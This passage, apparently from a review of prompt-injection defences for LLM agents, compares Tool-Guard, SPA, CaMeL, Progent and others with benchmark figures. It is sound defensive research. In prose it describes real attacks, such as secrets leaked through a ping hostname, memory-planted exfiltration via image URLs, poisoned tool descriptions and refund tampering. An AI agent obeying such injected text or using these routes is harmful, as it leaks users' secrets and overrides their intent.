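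If a poisoned weather tool leads the email agent to propose a message to the attacker, the check on arguments should fail, and `send_mail` moves to the second list. The planner then evaluates `send_mail` without the weather tool's description, so the tool list contains nothing that would prompt it to write to the attacker.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, Tool-Guard cut the attack success rate from 43.3% to 2.1%, while utility without an attack fell from 76.3% to 72.2%. On ASB, the attack success rate also fell close to zero. In tests with the smaller GPT-4o-mini, tasks took about 3.7 times as long and used about 1.5 times as many tokens. When the researchers kept the checks but removed the second list, attacks succeeded no more often but utility fell to 55.7%, so the isolation that list provides preserves utility and the security comes from the checks.

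Both checks accept a call by default and depend on a model's judgement, so Tool-Guard supports only a robustness claim. An attack that optimised the descriptions against the checks succeeded on 2.1% of tasks, but the researchers ran it on GPT-4o-mini, where it succeeded on only 15.5% of tasks without a defence. They argue that poisoned descriptions cannot reach the checks, but their published prompt for the first check includes the description of the proposed tool. Their published planning prompt also shows the model both lists at once, which would undermine the isolation if the experiments used that prompt.

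Girrens and Wang offer a stricter option in SPA, their system that checks a whole plan before running it. A model works out from the request alone which tools the task would need, and the planner writes a plan for these imaginary tools. A later stage matches them to installed ones. A malicious tool description might affect the matching, but it cannot add a step to the plan. In this mode, about three quarters of AgentDojo runs failed at the matching stage, and utility fell from 53.0% to 14.1% even with the label checks off.

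A developer who lets the planner read tool descriptions must either add whoever writes them to the trusted computing base or restrict tool calls with rules that do not depend on the descriptions.

### Local and remote tools

How much trust a tool requires also depends on where it runs. Anthropic points out that a user can read the code of a locally installed tool and pin its version, so the agent keeps using the copy the user reviewed. The trusted computing base then includes one known version of the tool. The operator of a remote tool can change it at any time after the user approves it, so the user has to trust the operator for as long as the agent uses the tool. The Model Context Protocol explicitly allows a server's list of tools to change.

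Software can remove part of this dependence. When the user approves a tool, the harness can store a cryptographic hash of its description, a short fingerprint that changes if the text does. It can then refuse the tool if the hash no longer matches. None of the frameworks that Shaikh and Montaruli examined compares descriptions over time.

A remote tool's code can change while its description stays the same. The tool might start returning injected text or keep a copy of everything the agent sends it. Label rules can address both problems if they treat the tool's results as untrusted and its operator as a recipient of the arguments. Anthropic advises users to try unreviewed remote tools on fake data first.

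A tool that is not malicious can still fetch malicious data. For example, a GitHub connector that passes every malware check can load a poisoned README file into the model's context. Anthropic favours inspecting results as they arrive, because the log of a successful theft shows only an authorised call.

### Memory that outlasts a session

Agents increasingly keep information between sessions in memory features, project instruction files and working folders. An injection saved in one of these places can affect the agent again whenever the agent loads it. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) describes an attack called MINJA that planted malicious memories using only ordinary queries, with an injection success rate of 98.2%. The survey covers work up to April 2026, and none of the benchmarks in it tested attacks across sessions.

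In an example from Girrens and Wang, a user asks an agent on Monday to find an invoice from Acme and keep its details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number and a malicious instruction. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the planner reads the stored invoice, the instruction can change Tuesday's plan. Even if the planner never reads it, a correct plan can send the money to the attacker's account.

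Many agents store a model's summary instead of the original text. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (2026) warns that the summary may drop the malicious wording and the source but keep the detail that triggers the harmful action. The invoice might become a note that Acme's account number has changed, which contains little for a detector to flag. The paper proposes keeping a record of each memory's source outside the model and checking it before risky actions.

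SPA stores each result in three parts: the value, its label and a description of what the value represents. Monday's planner writes that description before any tool runs. Tuesday's planner sees the description and the format of the data, but not the value. It can include a step that retrieves the invoice, and the software loads the value only when the plan runs. If *m* is the stored item and *c* is the label on any conditions that determined whether the step would run, the retrieved value gets the label

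ℓ(value) = ℓ(*m*) ⊔ *c*.

Storing data therefore never makes it more trusted. If the tool descriptions are honest, no attacker's text reaches a planner in any session. Monday's planner reads only trusted text, so the descriptions it writes are trustworthy. The only new text Tuesday's planner reads is those descriptions and the new request.

Girrens and Wang tested this by splitting each of AgentDojo's 97 original tasks into two to five successive requests. With label checks on, 0.2% of attacked runs counted as successful attacks, including two in which SPA had already rejected the plan. The checks reduced utility from 62.5% to 35.3%. When a later request needed a result that an earlier one had stored, its plan retrieved the result in 89.9% of cases.

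The low attack rate is weak evidence that SPA protects memory, because attacks succeeded in only 0.6% of runs even with the checks off and stored values shown directly to the planner. The researchers acknowledge that their attack only weakly tests delayed memory poisoning.

SPA's rules would block Tuesday's payment even if the invoice were genuine. *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (2026) proposes an exception in which stored data gains authority only if at least two independent trusted sources, such as an internal registry and a bank, confirm it or the user approves the specific action. Two copies of the same web page would not count. In both systems, the store of labels or origins becomes part of the trusted computing base, so the agent's file tools must not be able to edit it.

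### Permissions after a long history is shortened

The record of where text came from can also be lost within one session. When the history nears the model's length limit, the harness has a model summarise it and continues from the summary, a step known as compaction. The summary mixes the user's words with text from emails and tool results, so label rules would treat it as untrusted. *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026) found that Claude Code and Codex treat it as trusted. In all 1,108 automatic compactions the researchers recorded, the harness inserted the summary as a user message.

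This undermines any monitor that derives permissions from the latest user message. The researchers had Progent write a new policy for each request, because a policy fixed at the start let the agent complete a second task in only 7 of 60 sessions, compared with 41 when Progent wrote new ones. In one example, the user asks about spending in March, and a transaction record contains an instruction to pay the attacker. Progent refuses the payment because the question does not call for one. The summary then lists the blocked payment as unfinished work, and the next policy allows it, so the attacker gets paid even though Progent enforces that policy correctly.

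Stating the correct account number does not protect the user either. In another test, the user gave the landlord's account number and asked what a notice said. The notice, written by the attacker, gave a different number as plain information. After compaction, the user asked the agent to pay the rent. Policies based on the summary allowed a payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases when one model wrote the policies and 59% when a newer model did, while policies based on the user's own messages never allowed it. The newer summary-writing models almost always flagged injected instructions but rarely flagged a false account number, which looks much like a real one.

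Fei and colleagues prove that no improvement in the summaries can fully solve this. Let *p*_L be the probability that a system with no information about who wrote each piece of text allows a payment to an account in a legitimate record. Let *p*_A be the same probability when an attacker wrote the record. Then

*p*_L − *p*_A ≤ TV(*P*_L, *P*_A),

where *P*_L and *P*_A are the distributions of everything the system reads in the two cases. TV is the total variation distance, which is 0 for identical distributions and 1 for distributions that never overlap. An attacker who perfectly imitates legitimate records makes the distance 0, so the system accepts forgeries exactly as often as genuine records.

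The proposed solution gives the agent and the policy writer different inputs. The agent reads the summary, but the policy writer receives only exact copies of the user's messages. Software attaches a cryptographic tag to each message when it arrives. After compaction, a gate checks that the messages are genuine, in order and complete. Without the completeness check, an attacker could remove a later message that cancelled a request. If any check fails, the policy allows no tool calls. An attacker can therefore stop the agent from working but cannot shape its policy.

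The researchers tested the gate on 40 attacked AgentDojo runs. When the summary served as the user's message, the attacker succeeded in 7 runs and the agent completed 9 of the user's tasks. With the gate on and the summary presented as a tool result, no attack succeeded and the agent completed 19 tasks, compared with 27 without compaction. In six runs, the policy still allowed the attacker's call because the user's request had not specified the recipient. The gate cannot authenticate an account number that the user asks the agent to take from a document.

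This design adds the software that receives the user's messages, along with its keys and counters, to the trusted computing base, and the agent must not be able to reach any of them. In October 2026, OpenAI made a simpler change by having Codex's reviewing model attribute summaries to the assistant. In a test with a doctored summary, the earlier version approved 5 of 33 calls for the attacker and the new one approved none. Fei and colleagues built a similar filter, which worked as well as the gate within a single process. The filter failed when the history passed through a file that the agent could write to, because an attacker could replay old user messages there.

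### Reports from other agents

An agent may pass part of a job to a sub-agent. This can improve security if the sub-agent reads untrusted pages for the main agent, as a quarantined model does. However, Anthropic warns that delegation opens a new route for injections if the main agent trusts the sub-agent's report more than an ordinary tool result because it came from the same system.

A sub-agent that has read an attacker's page may repeat the attacker's instructions. *Trust propagation and structural containment in Multi-agent LLM pipelines* (2026) describes how an agent with few permissions can pass a forged message to one with more, which then acts on it. *When Child Inherits* (2026) cites earlier work in which some models resisted an injection when they received it directly but obeyed the same malicious request when it came from another agent.

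The main agent should trust a sub-agent's report according to where its contents came from. Under the usual label rules, the report carries the join of the labels on everything the sub-agent has read. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) enforces this. The main model cannot read the report without taking on its label, which then limits what the main model may do. Unlike a quarantined model, the sub-agent can use tools, because the same rules restrict its calls after it reads untrusted data. The designer has to trust the software that tracks the labels, but not the sub-agent's model.

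A sub-agent can also wrongly trust the main agent. Fei and colleagues found that in Claude Code, a sub-agent receives its task as a user message even though the main agent wrote it. If an injection has misled the main agent, the attacker's goal can reach the sub-agent as if the user had requested it. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) therefore requires a cryptographic record that traces each agent's authority back to a person who granted it. It also warns against giving sub-agents broader permissions than their tasks need.

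Claude Code's auto mode runs one classifier when the main agent delegates a task to a sub-agent and another when the sub-agent finishes. According to InfoQ (2026), the first checks whether the task matches the user's intent and can block it. The second examines the sub-agent's work, but Anthropic states that it can only issue a warning. The main agent may still follow an injected instruction in the sub-agent's report, so any guarantee has to come from fixed limits on the main agent's tool calls.

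## Robustness and enforcement compared

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, published in May 2026 and since revised, argues that enforcing limits on tool calls is worth the trouble. Developers may doubt this because the limits make an agent somewhat less useful and the newest models already resist most injections without them.

### The case against relying on the model

The paper argues that an agent's security should not depend on its model. It cites as precedents the failed defences of image classifiers and the adaptive attacks by Nasr and colleagues. It also notes that defenders have an option with agents that they lacked with image classifiers, because an agent's model acts only through a harness and tools, where software can check each action. Robust models still help, according to the paper, but the model should not be the only security boundary.

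One objection to enforcement is that robust models are enough. Defensive training can greatly reduce successful attacks, while enforcement requires engineering work and computing time and reduces the agent's utility. A developer can get the benefit of defensive training by switching to a better-trained model, without writing a policy.

The paper replies that requests are ambiguous. If the model alone decides what a request authorises, security depends on how it interprets the user's words, whereas an explicit policy sets limits that apply under any interpretation. However, someone has to derive the policy from the same ambiguous request, and the paper concedes that this problem is unsolved, which weakens its reply. The reply is strongest for limits that do not depend on the task, such as a ban on sending passwords to outside servers.

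The paper's other reply is that a model may refuse an injection on one run and obey it on the next. Removing the randomness would not stop attacks, because an attacker could still search for wording that produces the forbidden action every time. Adding a second model as a guard would not stop them either, since researchers have got past both models by combining text optimised against one with text optimised against the other. This is a stronger argument, but how much it matters depends on the harm a failure could cause. A small failure rate may be acceptable in an agent that drafts replies for a person to check, but not in one that can empty a bank account.

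### Eleven attacks on real products

As evidence, the paper examines eleven attacks on real agents and tools, including Microsoft 365 Copilot, OpenAI's Operator and the coding agents Devin and Cursor. For each attack, it identifies the security principles the product violated.

One attack used Memories, a ChatGPT feature that keeps information about the user for later conversations. An injection in a document or web page planted instructions in Memories through ChatGPT's macOS app. From then on, the app sent the user's conversations to the attacker's server by loading an invisible image whose web address contained the conversation text. The paper counts this as a failure of both tamper resistance, because the attacker's text changed storage that the app trusted, and secure information flow, because private text reached an outside server.

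The `ping` attack on Claude Code began with an instruction hidden in a code file. The agent read secrets such as API keys from the project's `.env` file, then ran `ping` with a hostname that contained them. Looking up that hostname sent the secrets to the attacker's server. The paper lists violations of secure information flow and least privilege, the latter because the agent could run shell commands with any arguments at any time. Complete mediation arguably belongs on the list too, since the approval check skipped `ping`.

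The paper's table links all eleven attacks to secure information flow, six to least privilege, three to complete mediation, and two each to tamper resistance and human error. These counts are approximate. For the attack on Cursor, for example, the table lists two principles but the text lists four. Almost any successful injection also violates secure information flow, because text from an untrusted source has influenced an important action. The principle's presence in every row is therefore weak evidence about whether a particular labelling system would have worked.

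The mapping is also retrospective. Nobody built the proposed defences and ran them against these attacks, so the study cannot show how many attacks the defences would have stopped or how much legitimate work they would have blocked. The sample is narrow too, because Johann Rehberger published ten of the eleven attacks. He also co-authored the earlier report by Christodorescu and colleagues that covers the same cases.

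The coding agent Amp could edit its own settings file, so an injection could add malicious commands to the list that ran automatically. Preventing Amp from changing that file looks easy and would have stopped this attack. An attack called AI ClickFix is much harder to prevent. In it, a web page led an agent to click a button that copied a malicious command, then to paste the command into a terminal. The paper suggests asking the user before an agent moves text from a browser to a terminal, but acknowledges that this restricts the agent and relies on the user to tell instructions from data.

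### Adaptive attacks on enforced defences

Most results for enforced defences come from fixed attacks, the kind of test that made many robustness-based defences look strong. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (June 2026), Narisetty, Kore and colleagues warned that the field might be repeating the mistake of relying on such tests. They compared the designs of seven systems, including CaMeL and FIDES, but attacked only Progent.

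The researchers attacked the language model that proposes changes to Progent's policy. Their injection described the malicious action as a routine, already authorised step, hoping the policy would expand to allow it. The agent and the policy model both used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model. They ran eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo environments with every injection task, and repeated the study three times. The table gives the average attack success rate per case.

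| Environment | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent withstood the attack, but the test was mild because it used a single hand-written template that was not optimised. The template's gentler wording may also have made the agent less likely to obey, which would explain why the template did worse than the standard attack. The workspace results are not evidence about Progent, because this model ignored the injections there even without a defence. Leaving them out gives averages of about 39%, 6% and 4%. In this setting, Progent also reduced the share of user tasks completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

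*AutoDojo* provides broader evidence, testing ten defences and five main target models. Its attacker is a language model that receives a ranked list of earlier injections and how often each one succeeded. In each of six rounds, it suggests why some worked better than others, writes a new injection and receives the result. It has no information about which defence the agent uses or what the user will ask, so it searches for text that works across many requests. The table shows results for GPT-4o-mini on three AgentDojo environments.

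| Defence | Fixed attack succeeds | AutoDojo succeeds | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| PIGuard (detector) | 0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| DataFilter (model that deletes injections) | 12.6% | 33.4% | 64.9% |
| DRIFT | 2.6% | 6.4% | 49.1% |
| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| ROPE | 6.4% | 4.4% | 59.6% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 26.3% |

ROPE blocks a call if a sensitive argument came from untrusted content rather than the user. Several of AutoDojo's researchers also worked on ROPE. Some rates are lower in the second column because AutoDojo must report a newly written injection, even if an older one worked better.

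One successful attack on PIGuard shows why detectors did worse. The user asked the agent to pay a bill. PIGuard removed the fixed attack's obvious commands from the bill. AutoDojo's version looked like an ordinary billing notice stating that the payee's account had changed and a small fee was due. It contained no obvious command, so PIGuard let it through and the agent paid the attacker.

The results suggest that enforced defences are harder for attackers to adapt to, but six rounds is a small budget compared with that of the search attack by Nasr and colleagues. AutoDojo also developed its injections against Progent and DRIFT using a different helper model from the one in the final test, so it reports the resulting rates as lower bounds.

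Another AutoDojo result supports the objection that robust models are enough. Against an agent running on Claude Haiku 4.5 with no added defence, AutoDojo succeeded in only 1.8% of cases. CaMeL reduced this to 0.5%, but it also cut the share of legitimate tasks completed from 70.2% to 40.4%. That reduction is not worthwhile unless the few attacks that succeed without CaMeL could do serious damage.

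Enforcement can be simple when the rule is narrow. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes an adaptive attacker that made more than 20,000 attempts to extract secrets under nine defence configurations. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. Ordinary code that checked each response before delivery let no secrets through in 15,000 attacks. That check covers only the model's replies, not the other actions an agent can take.

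### Broken guarantees, weak policies and uncovered attacks

When an attack succeeds despite an enforced defence, the fix depends on the cause. Let *E* be the set of actions the agent executed, *P* the set the policy allowed and *U* the set the user authorised.

- **Broken guarantee:** *E* is not contained in *P*. The agent did something the policy forbids, so the enforcing software has a flaw or the attacker found a way around it. The OpenAI–Hugging Face incident was a failure of this kind.
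- **Weak policy:** *E* is contained in *P* but not in *U*. The monitor worked, but its rules allowed too much.
- **Uncovered attack:** *E* is contained in both *P* and *U*, and harm still follows. The false summary in the email example is such an attack.

Narisetty and colleagues left open whether an attack could succeed using only tools that the policy already allows. In November 2026, Zhang, Bertran and colleagues published 90 test cases of such attacks in *Beyond Instruction Override*. The attacker tampers with the user's task instead of replacing it. In one case, an agent has to settle a dispute over a damaged item. The user tells it to take the refund amount from the platform's order record, which gives $899.99. The buyer's evidence gives $1,074.99, perhaps based on a false rule that refunds include a $175 repair cost. The agent needs the refund tool to pay either amount.

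Without a defence, these attacks succeeded in 17.0% of runs, averaged over five models. With Progent the rate was 15.4%. In a closer study of two of the models, Progent blocked eight of the agents' 116 harmful calls.

Progent's monitor applied the policies it had, so its guarantee held. In 52 of the 90 cases, the harm is in a structured argument such as an amount or an access level. The request specifies which source to rely on, so a stricter policy could have caught the wrong value. In the other 38 cases, the harm is in free text such as an email or a note explaining a decision. Rules about tools and recipients do not cover that text.

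CaMeL kept the attack success rate to 1.3%, using policies and trust labels that the researchers wrote for this test. But it completed only 13.3% of legitimate tasks, compared with 95.3% for the undefended agent. An agent that completes so few tasks gives an attacker few chances, so the low attack success rate is weak evidence that the policies were both strict and usable.

*INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, October 2026) reported results that seem to favour robustness. It tested agents whose only tool was the shell, and adapted Progent and the central idea of CaMeL to check shell commands. Neither adaptation measurably reduced attacks on any of five models, and the Progent version raised the rate for Claude Sonnet 4.6 from 6.5% to 27.1%. Replacing a 70-billion-parameter Llama model with Meta-SecAlign cut the rate from 29.6% to 7.8%.

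Nguyen and colleagues limit their conclusion to their own adaptations. A shell command can do far more than a tool with a fixed purpose, so a policy designed for named tools fits it badly. The scoring may also understate what enforcement achieved. A language model classified a run as compromised if the injection influenced the agent's actions or decisions, so a run could count as compromised even if the monitor had replaced the harmful command with a harmless one. The score therefore partly measures whether the attack misled the agent's model, which a monitor does not try to prevent. The results show that a developer cannot move a policy system to a shell agent and expect the same protection, but not that anyone broke either system's guarantee.

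### Harm without a forbidden action

*Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) compares an agent to a compiler, a program that translates source code into instructions for a machine. A correct compiler preserves the meaning of the source code, and a secure agent should preserve the user's intent. The paper divides this aim into four properties. Instruction integrity requires every action to trace back to the user's instructions. Data-flow integrity keeps data from reaching unauthorised destinations. Tool integrity means tools do only what they declare. Judgement integrity means planted text does not distort the agent's decisions.

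Suppose a user asks an agent to review a scientific paper, and the paper includes a sentence claiming that leading experts consider it the best work in its field. The agent then writes an overly favourable review, without following an injected command, leaking anything or making a forbidden tool call.

Let *J*(*q*, *d*) be the agent's decision on request *q* after reading data *d*, and let δ be added text that would not change a correct reasoner's answer. Judgement integrity requires

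*J*(*q*, *d* ⊕ δ) = *J*(*q*, *d*) for every such δ,

where ⊕ means inserting the text into the data. The boast about leading experts adds nothing to the paper's scientific content, so it should not change the score.

This condition compares decisions on two different inputs, so a monitor that observes only one run cannot check it, just as it cannot check noninterference. Separating the agent from the data would not work either, because the agent has to read the paper to review it. Someone must also decide which text is irrelevant. The definition gives little protection against an invented experimental result, which might change even a careful reviewer's conclusion.

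Zhang and colleagues instead draw the boundary by authority, counting planted text as an attack if it is meant to influence a decision that its source has no authority to make. A false statement on a subject the source is entitled to speak about is misinformation, which usually takes independent evidence to detect. By this test, researchers may report their results in a paper but not set the paper's score.

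Qu and colleagues rate CaMeL as fully enforcing instruction and data-flow integrity, but find that CaMeL, Progent and DRIFT do not protect judgement integrity at all. They give partial credit to filters that remove injected text, which are robustness-based and offer no guarantee. Tests by Zhang and colleagues suggest that such filters provide limited help. For two models, DRIFT's filter fully removed 78% to 85% of planted texts that told the agent what outcome to pursue, but only 26% to 34% of those that misstated a fact or misinterpreted a value, because such statements look like ordinary data. A developer can still limit the consequences of a biased judgement, for example by letting an agent that reviews a paper recommend a score but not accept the paper.

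### What the benchmarks leave out

Rigid defences look better on AgentDojo than they would in many real jobs. Only 6 of its 97 original tasks require a change of plan or policy, so a defence that can never change either loses at most about 6 percentage points of utility as a result. Xiang and colleagues argue that such benchmarks create a false sense of utility, and Progent's results support them. With GPT-4o-mini, Progent reduced utility by 3.5 points on the AgentDojo tasks that AutoDojo used. On AgentDyn, whose tasks are more open-ended, it reduced the share of tasks completed from 46.7% to 6.7%.

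AgentDojo also has few requests that leave the choice of action to outside content, such as "do everything on my to-do list". *AutoDojo* classes only 4 of the 57 tasks it used as such requests. These requests are the most dangerous for an undefended agent. With GPT-4o-mini, the fixed attack succeeded in 87.5% of these cases and 43.3% of cases where the request specified everything. Progent, DRIFT and ROPE kept success to 11% or less in both groups. But Progent and DRIFT often did so by allowing only tools that read data, which can also stop the agent from doing what is on the list.

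The attacks in common benchmarks make other defences look stronger than they are. When Claude Haiku 4.5 had no added defence, AgentDojo's fixed attack succeeded in 0.3% of cases, so any defence tested on that model would appear nearly perfect. Most benchmark attacks also try to redirect the agent to a new task, which creates an obvious mismatch for detectors to find. Zhang and colleagues found that attacks that directly stated the attacker's goal were among the three least successful types under every defence except CaMeL.

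Many of these comparisons also used small or older models. A stronger planner might lose less utility under CaMeL, and a better-trained model might resist more injections without CaMeL. The absolute rates are therefore poor predictors of how an agent built on a leading model from late 2026 would perform.

### The main methods side by side

The figures in this table come from different models and tests, so they do not rank the methods.

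| Method | Guarantee | Main assumptions | Best evidence | Cost | Known failure |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Defensive training (Meta-SecAlign) | None against new attacks | Training generalises, and the harness labels sources correctly | Attack success fell from 29.6% to 7.8% in a shell agent | About 2 points of utility for one Qwen model | An adaptive search succeeded in 96% of cases |
| Detectors (PIGuard) | None against new attacks | Injections look different from ordinary data | No fixed AgentDojo attack succeeded | Utility fell from 66.7% to 43.9% | AutoDojo succeeded in 28.0% of cases |
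| Sandboxes | Confined code cannot reach files or hosts outside the boundary | The kernel or hypervisor and the proxy are sound | Standard components held up in Anthropic's products | Users must grant exceptions or do without some functions | Theft through an approved host, and escapes by capable models |
| Tool-call policies (Progent) | Every executed call satisfies the policy | The policy is right and no call bypasses the monitor | AutoDojo succeeded in 7.7% of cases, against 52.4% without a defence | Utility fell from 46.7% to 6.7% on AgentDyn | Tampering with refunds and messages succeeded almost as often as without it |
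| Fixed plans with tracked values (CaMeL) | Untrusted text cannot add calls, and arguments satisfy the policy | The request and tool descriptions are honest, and the policies are right | AutoDojo succeeded in 0% to 1.8% of cases on five models | Utility fell from 66.7% to 26.3% with GPT-4o-mini | Leaks through a program's branches |
| Information-flow labels (FIDES) | No call violates the flow policy | All labels are correct | A fixed attack caused no policy violation on AgentDojo | About 23 points of utility with o1 | Secrets can leak through the choice of steps |

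### Designs that combine both

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* supports designs in which a model interprets and plans while independent software authorises every protected action. CaMeL works this way. ShieldAgent combines a model's reasoning about safety policies with checks that software can run. Claude Code offers a classifier, permission rules and an optional sandbox. The paper notes that these combinations do not all give the same guarantees.

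A second layer of defense helps only if it covers something the first one misses. Progent's rules did this for the Meta-SecAlign agent by stopping tool calls that the model had wrongly requested. DRIFT's layers did not complement each other against the attacks by Zhang and colleagues. With only DRIFT's filter, 6.6% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 98.0% of legitimate tasks. With DRIFT's checks on the plan and the arguments as well, 7.0% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 88.9% of legitimate tasks. Those checks looked mainly for departures from the plan, and these attacks used the tools the plan expected.

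Xiang and colleagues propose designing the two kinds of defence together. They recommend giving a judge model only structured records, which lets developers train it for that narrow job instead of trying to make it resist every possible text. Their proposal that a model report each instruction before following it would also let the harness discard the whole document containing an injection, or ask the user. Without such a report, a model trained to ignore the injection may still rely on the rest of the document, which the attacker may also have altered.

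In the refund case, a combined design could follow Zhang and colleagues' recommendation to accept each important tool argument only from a source with the authority to set it. Software would copy the amount from the order record, regardless of what the model inferred from the buyer's evidence. A model trained to resist manipulation would write the explanation, and a person could review unusual cases. A persuasive buyer might still get a misleading sentence into the explanation, but could not raise the refund above $899.99 as long as the order record was correct and no other tool could pay out money.
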